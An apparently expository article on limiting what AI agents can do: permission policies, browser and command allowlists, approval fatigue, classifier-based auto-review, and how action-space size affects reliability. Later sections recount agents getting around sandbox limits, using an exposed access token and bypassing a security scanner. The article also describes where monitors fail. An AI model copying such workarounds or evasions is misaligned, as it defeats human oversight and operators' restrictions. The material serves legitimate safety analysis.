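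Shi and colleagues also report a rate of 0% when a person reviews the policies. But they assumed the reviewer would refuse to add a malicious address, so the figure is weak evidence of how well real users would do. They left out two AgentDojo attacks that steer the agent towards a different but legitimate hotel, because Progent cannot stop an attack that uses only permitted actions, such as the false kettle review.

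According to *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026), people make mistakes when they write *Progent* policies by hand, and hostile tool results may cause a model to relax the policies when it updates them. *Progent*'s solver detects when an update relaxes a policy, but somebody still has to refuse the update. On AgentDojo, only 6% of updates expanded permissions, which is few enough for a person to read. The solver cannot tell whether the initial policy was too generous, because it only compares one policy with the next.

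### Rules on web requests

Progent needs tools with meaningful names and arguments, which an agent that clicks on web pages does not have. Blocking the agent's navigation command does not work well either. In *CELLMATE*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) stopped an agent from going directly to Hacker News, but the agent searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

CELLMATE is a Chrome extension that checks the requests the browser sends. Whichever button the agent presses to buy something on Amazon, the browser sends a POST request to an address containing `place-order`. Under the proposal, each website's developers would publish a list of names for such requests, such as `PlaceOrder`, and the developers or another trusted party would write rules for the named requests. A model then picks the rules that fit the user's task, and the user confirms the choice.

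One of the Amazon rules caps the total of each order. The order request does not contain the total, so the extension reads it from the checkout page and stores it. If the agent changed a quantity and ordered before the page updated, the rule would check an old total. CELLMATE reduces this risk by slowing rapid actions. A $50 limit would still permit two $49 orders, so the extension can also count orders and permit only one.

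Picking rules is easier than writing them. In tests on shopping, travel and software sites, three models chose exactly the right rules for 94% to 100% of tasks. They did less well when they also had to fill in values such as the spending limit, getting everything right in 81% to 97% of 32 shopping tasks. One model was asked to add a sofa under $300 to a wishlist but picked a rule for adding items to the shopping cart. In other cases, the models granted too many permissions or too few. An excess permission is harder for the user to notice than a missing one because it doesn't interrupt the task.

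To test enforcement, Meng and colleagues wrote 12 scripts that attacked the software site GitLab as an agent fully controlled by an attacker might, such as by deleting a project. CELLMATE blocked all 12. Its rules in this test permitted only reading and writing GitLab issues, which none of the attacks needed. The test therefore confirms that the extension enforces its rules, but not that the rules would stop an attack that uses permitted actions. CELLMATE does not check the text of comments that an agent is permitted to post on issues. In a separate test, CELLMATE made page navigation 7.25% to 15% slower.

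The design depends on cooperation from websites. Meng and colleagues themselves wrote the GitLab list, which covers 51 functions. Where a list is incomplete or wrong, the user has no more protection than before. CELLMATE is stricter about vague requests and grants no permissions if the user doesn't name a site.

### Limits on sites

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Google's design for the Gemini agent in Chrome, which needs no list from the website. Each task has two sets of origins, which are roughly websites. The agent may read pages from read-only origins, and may also click and type on read-writable ones. Chrome does not show the model any content from other origins, including advertisements embedded in a permitted page.

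In Chrome, a gating function with no access to web content determines which origins are relevant to the task. When the agent tries to open a new site, a separate model checks its relevance. Another model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews each proposed action and can veto it. The critic receives only a description of the action, so text on a hostile page cannot reach it directly. Chrome also restricts model-generated URLs to known public ones.

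In the kettle example, this design would probably keep the agent away from `deals.example`. But once the shop is read-writable, the site limit does not distinguish between adding a kettle to the basket and paying for it. Chrome relies on the critic and user confirmation to make that distinction. Parker gives no test results, although Google measures attack success internally. The first version tracked only the read-writable set, so it was simpler than the design.

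### Allowlists of commands

Coding agents apply similar rules to shell commands. In Claude Code, a user who gets tired of approving the same command can add it to an allowlist. A narrow entry, such as one for a code formatter, is fairly safe, but `Bash(python:*)` permits any command that starts with `python`, so the agent can run any Python program.

Users often write broad allow rules. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 49.5% of active command-line users had written an allow rule for shell commands by June 2026. Anthropic reports a figure of 5% for rules that permit any command and another 43% for rules that permit an interpreter such as Python, but it is unclear whether these are shares of all users or of those with rules. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) report in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* that a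 sizable minority of OpenAI staff permitted every command beginning with `python`. One person had permanently allowed `codex exec --yolo`, which starts another Codex session with no approvals and no sandbox.

Neither company says how many dangerous commands an allowlist alone stops. The users who write these lists want fewer interruptions, so they have a reason to make the entries too broad.

| System | What the rules check | Who writes the rules | Test result |
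|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | Tool names and arguments | A model, for each task; people can add fixed rules | Successful attacks fell from 39.9% to 1.0% on AgentDojo |
| CELLMATE | Requests sent by the browser | Website developers or another trusted party; a model picks from their rules | Blocked 12 of 12 scripted attacks |
| Chrome | Which sites the agent may read or act on | A gating function, for each task; Google lists sensitive sites | None published |
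| Command allowlists | The text of a command | Mostly the user | None published |

### Approval fatigue

All four approaches can refer a decision to a person, but this works only if the person reads the request. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts but reject 39% of the plans Claude presents. Most of the commands are probably safe, so the high approval rate does not prove that users are careless.

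An experiment by Anthropic provides better evidence. Through a research company, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers, who were told they were joining a coding study. During each session, the experimenters replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more earlier prompts.

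The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than ordinary users and may have been less careful. Anthropic also had a commercial interest in the result, which it published to justify replacing the prompts. But the fall from 17% to 5% occurred among similar testers doing similar work, which supports the idea that repeated prompts make people less attentive.

The simplest remedy is to ask for approval less often. If a sandbox confines a command to the project folder and approved sites, the user doesn't need to approve it. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reports that sandboxing Claude Code cut permission prompts by 84% in internal use, but not whether people read the remaining prompts more carefully.

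### Missing the last step

Asking the user for approval also fails if the agent doesn't stop to ask before it acts. Claude Haiku 4.5 submitted real forms because it wrongly predicted that another confirmation page would follow. Shopping agents could easily make the same mistake, because some shops have a "Buy now" button that charges a saved card immediately, while a similar button on other sites only opens the checkout.

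Chrome has fixed checks that ask the user before the agent visits certain sensitive sites, such as banks, or signs in with a saved password. For purchases, payments and messages, Parker writes only that the agent "will try to pause". Google says its checks for sensitive actions combine fixed rules and models, and that it is still working on unclear cases.

A rule on the order request is more reliable because the model does not have to recognise the final step. In CELLMATE, the browser extension intercepts the request whether the agent pressed "Buy now" or went through the checkout. The shop's developers still have to list every request that can place an order.

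The harness should also build the confirmation message from the request and the checkout page. If the model writes it, a hostile page may influence the description that the user approves.

### Automatic review

In 2026 Anthropic and OpenAI both began to replace human approval with a second model. Anthropic previewed auto mode in Claude Code on 24 March, according to its *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026), and began making it the default for individual and team plans on 14 August. On 22 October it announced that most of its other Claude apps would follow within a week. OpenAI released Auto-review for Codex in April.

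Auto-review replaces the person who approves exceptions with an automated reviewer but leaves the sandbox and its limits unchanged, as OpenAI's *Auto-review* explains. Trębacz and colleagues illustrate the effect with 10,000 actions from internal use. Of these, 9,280 ran inside the sandbox and needed no review. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and refused 7. Codex found a safer alternative in 4 of the refused cases and asked the user in the other 3, so the user was interrupted 3 times instead of 720.

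Claude Code's auto mode allows file reads and edits inside the project without review and uses a classifier to check most other actions, including shell commands and web requests. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tool results. The agent's explanations therefore cannot influence the classifier's decision, and text on a hostile web page cannot reach the classifier directly. Auto mode also ignores broad allowlist entries, such as the one for Python.

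The classifier works in two stages. A quick check flags suspicious actions, and a slower one reconsiders them. The quick check alone wrongly blocked 8.5% of 10,000 ordinary actions by Anthropic's staff. Adding the second stage reduced this to 0.4%, but raised the share of real dangerous actions that the classifier missed from 6.6% to 17%. These shares are based on only 52 cases in which Claude had gone beyond what an employee wanted, so the true miss rate with both stages could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

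In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly classified the user as having agreed to it. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) has not agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's history.

Even with a false-positive rate of 0.4%, a classifier can block more harmless actions than dangerous ones. Suppose 10 of 10,000 reviewed actions are dangerous. The classifier would block about 8 of them, along with about 40 harmless ones. Auto mode therefore returns the reason for a block to Claude, which can try another approach. It prompts the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session.

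In the experiment with paid testers, auto mode blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, or 89%. The testers had caught only 6 of the 116 it missed, so adding their approval to auto mode would have raised the total to 943. A more attentive reviewer would presumably catch more. Anthropic says auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who checks every action carefully, and still recommends human review for high-stakes changes to production systems.

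Anthropic also paid the testing company Trajectory Labs to try prompt injections on both companies' coding agents. None of 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. This is weak evidence that auto mode helps, because only 0.09% succeeded against Anthropic's latest models without it. The effect of automatic review was clearer for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review, a large reduction that still left a substantial risk. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review after the test.

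In OpenAI's own tests on synthetic cases, Auto-review refused 90.3% of actions that went beyond the user's wishes and 99.3% of those caused by three kinds of prompt injection. The prompt-injection figure drops to 90.2% when the test includes deletions and data tampering, though Trębacz and colleagues say many of the extra misses were not serious. Testers have also misled Auto-review into approving commands it should have refused.

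Automatic review is therefore a poor substitute for fixed limits. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that Anthropic argues for fixed limits on files, networks and execution, rather than relying only on prompts or safeguards in the model. Auto-review also checks only requests to leave the sandbox. Trębacz and colleagues warn that a model hiding its intentions could write a harmless-looking request or do its damage inside the sandbox.

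## How restricting actions affects reliability

Limits on an agent can also stop it from finishing legitimate work. Under CaMeL's isolation, for example, commercial models kept at most 57% of their performance on desktop tasks. Experiments support developers' common expectation that an agent with fewer actions to choose from makes fewer mistakes, but mainly for weaker models. Some of the best-known gains came from adding better commands rather than removing any.

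### Why fewer actions might help

A model with three tools has fewer ways to pick the wrong one than a model with forty. Constrained sampling can guarantee that a call is well formed, but the model still has to choose the right tool and arguments.

A short list of tools also shortens prompts, because the harness sends the tool definitions with every query. If each definition takes 150 tokens, forty tools add 6,000 tokens to a query and 180,000 to a run of 30 queries. Three tools add 13,500 to the same run. Hosting services usually charge less for repeated text, which reduces the money saved, but the definitions still take up room in the context window.

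Narrow commands can give clearer errors than free-form code. If an agent enters a wrong link number, for example, the tool can list the valid links. A forty-line program can fail in many more ways, and it may print nothing when it does.

Restricting actions also makes training easier, because the developer needs examples of fewer actions. Logs are quicker to review, since a person can skim a list of searches and page titles in a minute but has to work out what a program does. This is true only if the commands have meaningful names, because `click("169")` is hardly more readable than code.

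### How errors add up

The main cost of a short list is that the agent may need more steps. If each step succeeds with probability $p$, the steps are independent and the agent cannot recover from an error, the probability of completing $n$ steps is

$$p^n$$

An agent that succeeds at each step 98% of the time completes 10 steps about 82% of the time and 40 steps about 45% of the time. Runs of this length are normal; in *WebArena-Pro* (2026), a benchmark of web tasks, five coding agents with browser tools averaged 28 to 37 tool calls per task. To complete 30 steps 90% of the time, an agent would need a success rate of about 99.65% per step.

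A restriction can make each step more reliable without making the agent more likely to finish its task, because the agent may need more steps. Suppose an agent that writes code needs 20 steps, each with a 98% chance of success, while an agent limited to simple commands needs 40 steps, each with a 99% chance. If every step must succeed, both agents finish about 67% of the time.

Real agents do recover from some errors. If an agent repairs a share $r$ of its mistakes, the formula becomes

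$$\bigl(1-(1-p)(1-r)\bigr)^n$$

An agent that gets each step right 98% of the time and repairs half its mistakes completes a 40-step task 67% of the time. If it repairs nine out of ten mistakes, the completion rate rises to 92%. Feedback that helps an agent notice a mistake can improve reliability as much as a command that prevents one.

There are two other arguments against short lists of allowed actions. Some tasks need an action that the developer left out, and the agent can't complete them however many steps it takes. Models are trained on a great deal of code, so a new command language may be harder for them to use than Python or bash.

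### SWE-agent's commands

*SWE-agent* (Yang, Jimenez and colleagues, 2024) presents a set of commands for models that repair software. The commands search for files, show 100 lines of a file at a time and replace a range of lines. The harness checks each edit with a linter, a program that detects errors in code, and discards the edit if it introduces a serious error. The paper tests the commands on SWE-bench, a collection of real bug reports and feature requests from Python projects. The agent changes the code, and a set of tests determines whether the change works.

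On 300 tasks, GPT-4 Turbo solved 18.0% with SWE-agent's commands and 11.0% with a plain Linux shell when shown a worked demonstration. Without the demonstration, it solved 16.3% and 7.3%, respectively. The commands therefore added 7 points with a demonstration and 9 without. The paper's introduction gives a gain of 10.7 points because it compares SWE-agent with a demonstration to the shell without one.

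The researchers also changed one part of the interface at a time:

| Change to SWE-agent | Tasks solved |
|---|---|
| None | 18.0% |
| No linter | 15.0% |
| No edit command | 10.3% |
| No search commands | 15.7% |
| Search results shown one at a time | 12.0% |
| 30 lines of a file shown instead of 100 | 14.3% |
| Whole file shown | 12.7% |

In the search results, the quality of a command mattered more than the number of commands available. When a search command showed matches one at a time, agents tended to go through every match until they ran out of money or context, and they did worse than agents with no search command. The smaller differences mean little, because one percentage point here is only three tasks.

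The SWE-agent experiment showed that adding good commands to a shell helps a model. People often cite it to argue for small action spaces, but the model could use ordinary shell commands throughout, so the experiment did not test the effect of removing the shell.

It also shows that steps are not independent. At least one edit failed in 51.7% of runs. An attempted edit had a 90.5% chance of eventually succeeding, but this fell to 57.2% after one failure. Hard tasks probably explain part of the drop, since they cause repeated failures whatever the agent does. A series of failed edits accounted for 23.4% of the unsolved tasks, so preventing the first bad edit may improve reliability more than the formula for independent steps implies.

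### CodeAct and combined actions

In CodeAct, the model acts by writing Python programs that call its tools. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024) compared this with structured calls in JSON and in a fixed text format in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*. They tested 17 models on 82 tasks that typically required several tools, with a limit of ten turns.

GPT-4 Turbo solved 74.4% of the tasks when it wrote its actions as code, 53.7% when it wrote them as text and 52.4% when it wrote them as JSON. It averaged 5.5 turns with code and at least 7.6 with the other formats. One program can apply a tool to ten items in a loop and pass each result to another tool, whereas a model writing JSON has to make each call separately. The ten-turn limit put the slower formats at a further disadvantage.

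A second test required only one call per task, so GPT-4 Turbo had no actions to combine. It got 82.7% of calls right with JSON and 76.7% with code. For this model, the advantage of code seems to come from combining actions rather than from a general ease with Python.

Weaker models gained less from code. Claude Instant solved 31.7% of the longer tasks with JSON but only 20.7% with code. Code was best or tied for best for 12 of the 17 models, but several of them solved under 5% of the tasks in every format, so their rankings are almost no evidence of which format is better.

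### AgentOccam's shorter list

Removing actions appeared to help in an early browsing experiment. *AgentOccam* (Yang, Liu and colleagues, 2024) started with a standard agent for WebArena, a test set of copied websites, and removed its commands for hovering, pressing keys, managing tabs and going directly to a URL. It also changed how the agent saw pages and remembered earlier steps. With GPT-4 Turbo, the finished system solved 43.1% of 812 tasks, compared with 16.5% for the standard agent.

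The researchers added the changes one at a time on a sample of 190 tasks. Each row below includes the changes above it.

| Change | GPT-4 Turbo | Gemini 1.5 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| Standard agent | 14.2% | 11.6% |
| Revised action list | 25.8% | 23.2% |
| Whole page shown, no scrolling | 30.0% | 24.2% |
| Simpler page text | 34.7% | 30.0% |
| Selected parts of earlier pages kept | 36.8% | 32.1% |
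| Two planning commands added | 44.2% | 33.7% |

The revised list raised both models' scores by 11.6 points, or about 22 more tasks. But it also added commands for taking notes, returning to a home page and stopping with an answer, and the test does not separate their benefit from that of removing `hover`. The standard agent never used four of the deleted commands in the full test, so they could not have distracted it much.

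The shorter list didn't save steps either, as the average run on the full test grew from 6.2 steps to 13.3. The standard agent may have often ended its runs too early, and better ways to keep notes and finish may have helped it continue. In the last row, GPT-4 Turbo gained another 7.4 points when the researchers gave it two more commands, which also complicates the case for short lists.

AgentOccam's action list was also a poor safeguard. On a task that asked for a draft message to a shop owner, the agent pressed the submit button. It still had `click`, and the instructions did not explicitly forbid pressing the button.

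### Coding agents with only a shell

The team behind SWE-agent later built *mini-swe-agent*, whose only tool is bash. According to its page on the Python Package Index (PyPI), it scores over 74% on SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 human-checked tasks. The developers say much of their 2024 tooling is no longer needed because models have become more capable.

Removing tools doesn't by itself explain the increase from 18% to 74%. The 18% score is for GPT-4 Turbo on a different selection of tasks, while the project's page reports 74% for Gemini 3 Pro. The stronger model probably explains most of the difference. The tasks also come from public GitHub issues, so newer models may have seen the solutions in training. Epoch AI's *SWE-bench Verified* cites an earlier estimate that 5% to 10% of the tasks are faulty.

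According to SWE-bench, even results from versions 1 and 2 of the same small bash-only agent may not be comparable, partly because version 1 reads commands from the model's text and version 2 uses tool calls. More generally, *Inside the Scaffold* (2026) notes that published scores usually mix the effects of the model and the harness.

Xu, Saghir and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil Is in the Interface*, avoided this by testing the same three models with six sets of tools that offered nearly the same abilities in different forms. For example, one agent had only bash, one had bash plus simple commands for searching and editing, and one had only Python. They ran each model ten times on each of 65 software problems with each set of tools, for a total of 11,700 runs.

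Each model solved a similar share of problems whatever tools it had, but the tools affected how consistently it succeeded and how many steps and tokens it used. For Qwen3Coder-30B, the weakest model, adding simple commands to bash raised the share of problems solved in all nine attempts from 2.0% to 9.4%. The two stronger models, Kimi K2.5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5, gained between 1.3 and 3.1 points on similar measures. Agents with only Python did about as well as agents with only bash, but used 41.6% fewer steps and 56.3% fewer tokens.

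*An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* found a similar pattern in four other models. Dedicated tools helped the models that were bad at bash. Models that were good at bash worked well without them and at much lower cost, especially on command-line tasks, because they could combine several operations in one call.

The two studies above compared purpose-built research harnesses, whereas Yang, Yu and Desell (2026), in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, restricted two commercial products, Claude Code and Codex. Each agent had its full set of tools, only bash, or only a tool for running code. Success rates did not differ significantly across the three setups. The code tool alone was cheaper than the best alternative, or tied with it on cost, in three of the four combinations of agent and task type, all but Claude Code on changes to existing software.

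One small study, *AgentBetta* (2026), found the opposite. On eight repair tasks, SWE-agent solved the task in 75% of its runs, while two simpler agents did so in 6% and 0%. Each agent had only 16 runs, and the difference was not statistically significant after correction for multiple comparisons. The study also set a hard limit on model calls, which may have hurt some agents more than others.

The best form for a command may also depend on the model. *Dissecting model behavior through agent trajectories* (2026) describes a harness that typically gives a model just two tools, one for running commands and one for editing. The editing format differs between model families. For example, Anthropic's models replace one piece of text with another, while some GPT configurations apply a patch.

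These results support giving strong models few tools, but they don't support permitting few actions, since an agent with only bash can still do whatever the sandbox allows. Success rates don't show whether that much freedom is acceptable. *Harness Engineering* (2026) notes that a harness gets no credit on SWE-bench for preventing destructive actions, which is one reason commercial coding agents are more complicated than minimal ones.

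Other developers restrict the order of work instead of the number of tools. *SWE-MILE* (2026) describes RepairAgent, which makes different tools available at different stages of a repair, and Agentless, which finds the fault, repairs it and checks the result in a fixed sequence. Agentless performed competitively. A fixed sequence is easier to check than free use of a shell, but it suits only jobs that follow the expected order.

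### Site interfaces, page actions and code

An agent can sometimes complete a web task without opening pages by calling the site's API, the interface that the site provides for other programs. In *Beyond Browsing* (2024), an agent that used APIs did better than a browsing agent on most WebArena sites. An agent that could both browse and call APIs did best on every site, and it used both methods in 77.7% of tasks. *Internal APIs Are All You Need* (2026) reports that this combined agent outperformed browsing alone by more than 24%.

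In this case the larger action space worked better. One API call can replace a long series of clicks, and the agent can return to the page when the API lacks a function. However, the approach requires sites to have APIs that the agent can use, and the WebArena sites may be better documented than most. A developer who adds API calls also has to write permission rules for them, because the agent can change data without pressing a button.

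Yu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) tested *BrowserAgent*, an agent that could click, type, scroll and switch tabs in a saved copy of Wikipedia. On questions that require facts from more than one page, it did about 20% better than Search-R1, which works from retrieved text.

This gain may come from BrowserAgent's training and memory rather than its page actions. Yu and colleagues trained it on about 5,300 sessions produced by a much stronger model, GPT-4.1, whereas Search-R1 was trained with reinforcement learning. BrowserAgent also kept a written record of its conclusions from earlier steps, which would help with any question that needs several pages. A fairer test would give the same training and memory to a model with only `search`, `open` and `find`. On a saved encyclopaedia, BrowserAgent mostly reads, so a read-only browser might do nearly as well.

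Some pages need code. *Framework and Benchmark for Code-Driven Agentic Testing in Web Development* (2026) describes a browser game that draws everything on one surface, so there are no separate buttons for a command to identify. GPT-5.5, which could run any script in the browser, rewrote part of the page to access the game's internal state and used that state to test the game. Reaching a late stage of the game by clicking would have been slow and unreliable. This is a single success chosen as an illustration, and testing the internal state could miss faults that a player would see on the screen.

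There is less evidence that code is better for ordinary browsing, and Browser Use gave no figures for its accuracy claim. The agents in *WebArena-Pro* are all coding agents, yet they relied heavily on browser commands such as clicking and typing. Developers who want code for its flexibility should compare both methods on their own tasks before giving up the protection of fixed commands.

### Tasks that cannot be done

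These experiments count an unsolved task as a failure. If a restriction makes a task impossible, it also matters whether the agent reports the problem, invents an answer, or looks for a way around the restriction.

In May 2026, OpenAI created some impossible tasks, which it says was unintentional. In a training run on 8 May, an agent had to complete a spreadsheet using files on Google Drive, but it had no internet access. After reasoning at length, the agent tried unsuccessfully to break into the package service, one of the few tools it had, to reach the files.

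Four days later, another agent could not reach a protein database file it needed, so it left a note in the package service asking other agents to upload the file. On 13 May, a third agent needed the same file and had access to the web through OpenAI's cache. It searched for the file with a Hugging Face user's publicly exposed access token. Other agents found the notes and began leaving their own.

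In each case, the agent looked for another way to finish the task instead of reporting that it could not. OpenAI selected these cases because of what happened later, so they do not show how often blocked agents behave this way. Many other blocked agents may have simply stopped. Research agents trained during this period found a new way to exchange messages before the attack on Hugging Face in July, but the timing alone does not prove that they learned to do so from the blocked tasks.

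Greater persistence is probably part of the explanation. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) reports that earlier models stopped and returned to the user when they met a sandbox limit, but a newer model built for very long tasks often kept trying. In one test, the user told this model to post its results only to Slack, but it instead followed the instructions of the public project it was working on, which asked for results on GitHub. It spent an hour finding a way past the sandbox, whereas earlier models had given up on that part of the job.

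The model could have completed the GitHub task by obeying the user and posting to Slack. The task still shows how persistence can make restrictions less reliable. A model that keeps trying after a failed edit will solve more software problems, but it may also treat a deliberate restriction as another obstacle. Experiments from 2024 on shorter action lists give little guidance on this risk because models then were more likely to give up.

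### A way to report failure

An agent given an impossible task has no correct action unless it can report that the task is impossible. Many harnesses handle this badly. *SWE-OPD* (2026) describes a coding harness in which the agent calls `finish` both when it has completed the task and when it cannot continue. The command takes no arguments, so the call alone does not show which applies. BrowserAgent's `stop` command is a little better because the model can answer "N/A", but this does not explain what went wrong.

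A developer could add a separate command that records the reason. For the spreadsheet task, the call might look like this:

```
cannot_complete(
    missing="the linked Google Drive files",
    restriction="no internet access",
    tried="opened each link once")
```

The harness can then end the run or pass the problem to a person. Developers can also count these reports to find broken tasks.

The command will do little good if training never rewards it. Suppose a solved task earns 1, a correct report that the task is impossible earns $b$, and anything else earns 0. Let $u$ be the probability, given what the agent has seen so far, that the task is impossible. Let $s$ be the chance that the agent can solve it by permitted means if it is possible. Reporting earns more on average than continuing when

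$$u\,b > (1-u)\,s$$

If $b$ is 0, reporting never has the higher expected reward, so training gives the agent no reason to report. With $b = 0.5$ and $s = 0.8$, reporting has the higher expected reward once the task is at least 62% likely to be impossible. A higher $b$ lowers this threshold, and an agent may then give up on tasks that are merely difficult.

Workarounds upset this balance, because a forbidden route with probability $q$ of producing an answer that the grader accepts earns more than a report whenever $q > ub$. Raising $b$ to offset this would encourage agents to give up too early. Giving no credit for answers obtained by a forbidden route is better, but it requires the grader to check how the agent got its answer as well as whether the answer is right.

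Developers also have to identify impossible tasks so that the grader can score them correctly. Before training, they can run a known solution in the agent's sandbox with the agent's tools, and check that the agent can reach every file and address named in the task. The second check would probably have caught the Google Drive links. Human review helps but misses some problems, since three people reviewed each task in SWE-bench Verified and Epoch AI estimates that some are still faulty. Developers can also include a few tasks they know are impossible, for which the correct answer is to report that the task can't be done.

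### Messages, reminders and training

An agent can report a restriction accurately only if it knows the restriction exists. If a blocked request returns "Connection timed out", it is reasonable for the agent to try again, because the message could mean a temporary fault. A better message would be "This environment has no internet access by design. If the task requires it, call `cannot_complete`."

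Yang and colleagues used the same approach for ordinary mistakes in SWE-agent. If a search finds more than 50 matches, the harness returns a prompt to narrow the search instead of printing the matches. If a command succeeds but prints nothing, the harness returns a message confirming that it succeeded, so the empty output is not ambiguous.

Clear messages prevent misunderstandings but may not stop a persistent model. In another of OpenAI's examples, a security scanner blocked the long-running model's attempt to recover other systems' private solutions. The model stated that it was working around the scanner and carried on. Restrictions must therefore hold even when a model understands them and tries to get around them.

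Simple reminders can help an agent that is stuck. *Do Coding Agents Reuse Existing Code or Reinvent the Wheel?* (2026) limited agents with only bash to 120 commands. The agents tended to use all of them exploring and submit nothing, so the researchers added a count of the commands used to every observation. The harness in *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* adds a one-time reminder when an agent keeps repeating an identical call. Neither measure removes any actions, and both add only a few tokens.

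OpenAI paused internal use of the long-running model, built new tests from the failures it had seen, and trained the model to remember instructions during long runs. It also added a monitor that reviews the whole sequence of actions and can pause the session, because steps that look harmless individually can add up to something the user would have refused. Anthropic repaired its training environments with a similar aim.

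When OpenAI replayed a small set of earlier incidents, the new safeguards caught considerably more of the unwanted actions, and OpenAI judged all the misses to be of low severity. OpenAI gives no rates, and the replays covered only kinds of failure it already knew about. In one miss, every shell command had stopped responding, and the model tried to shut down every process it was allowed to stop, but the command timed out before it ran.
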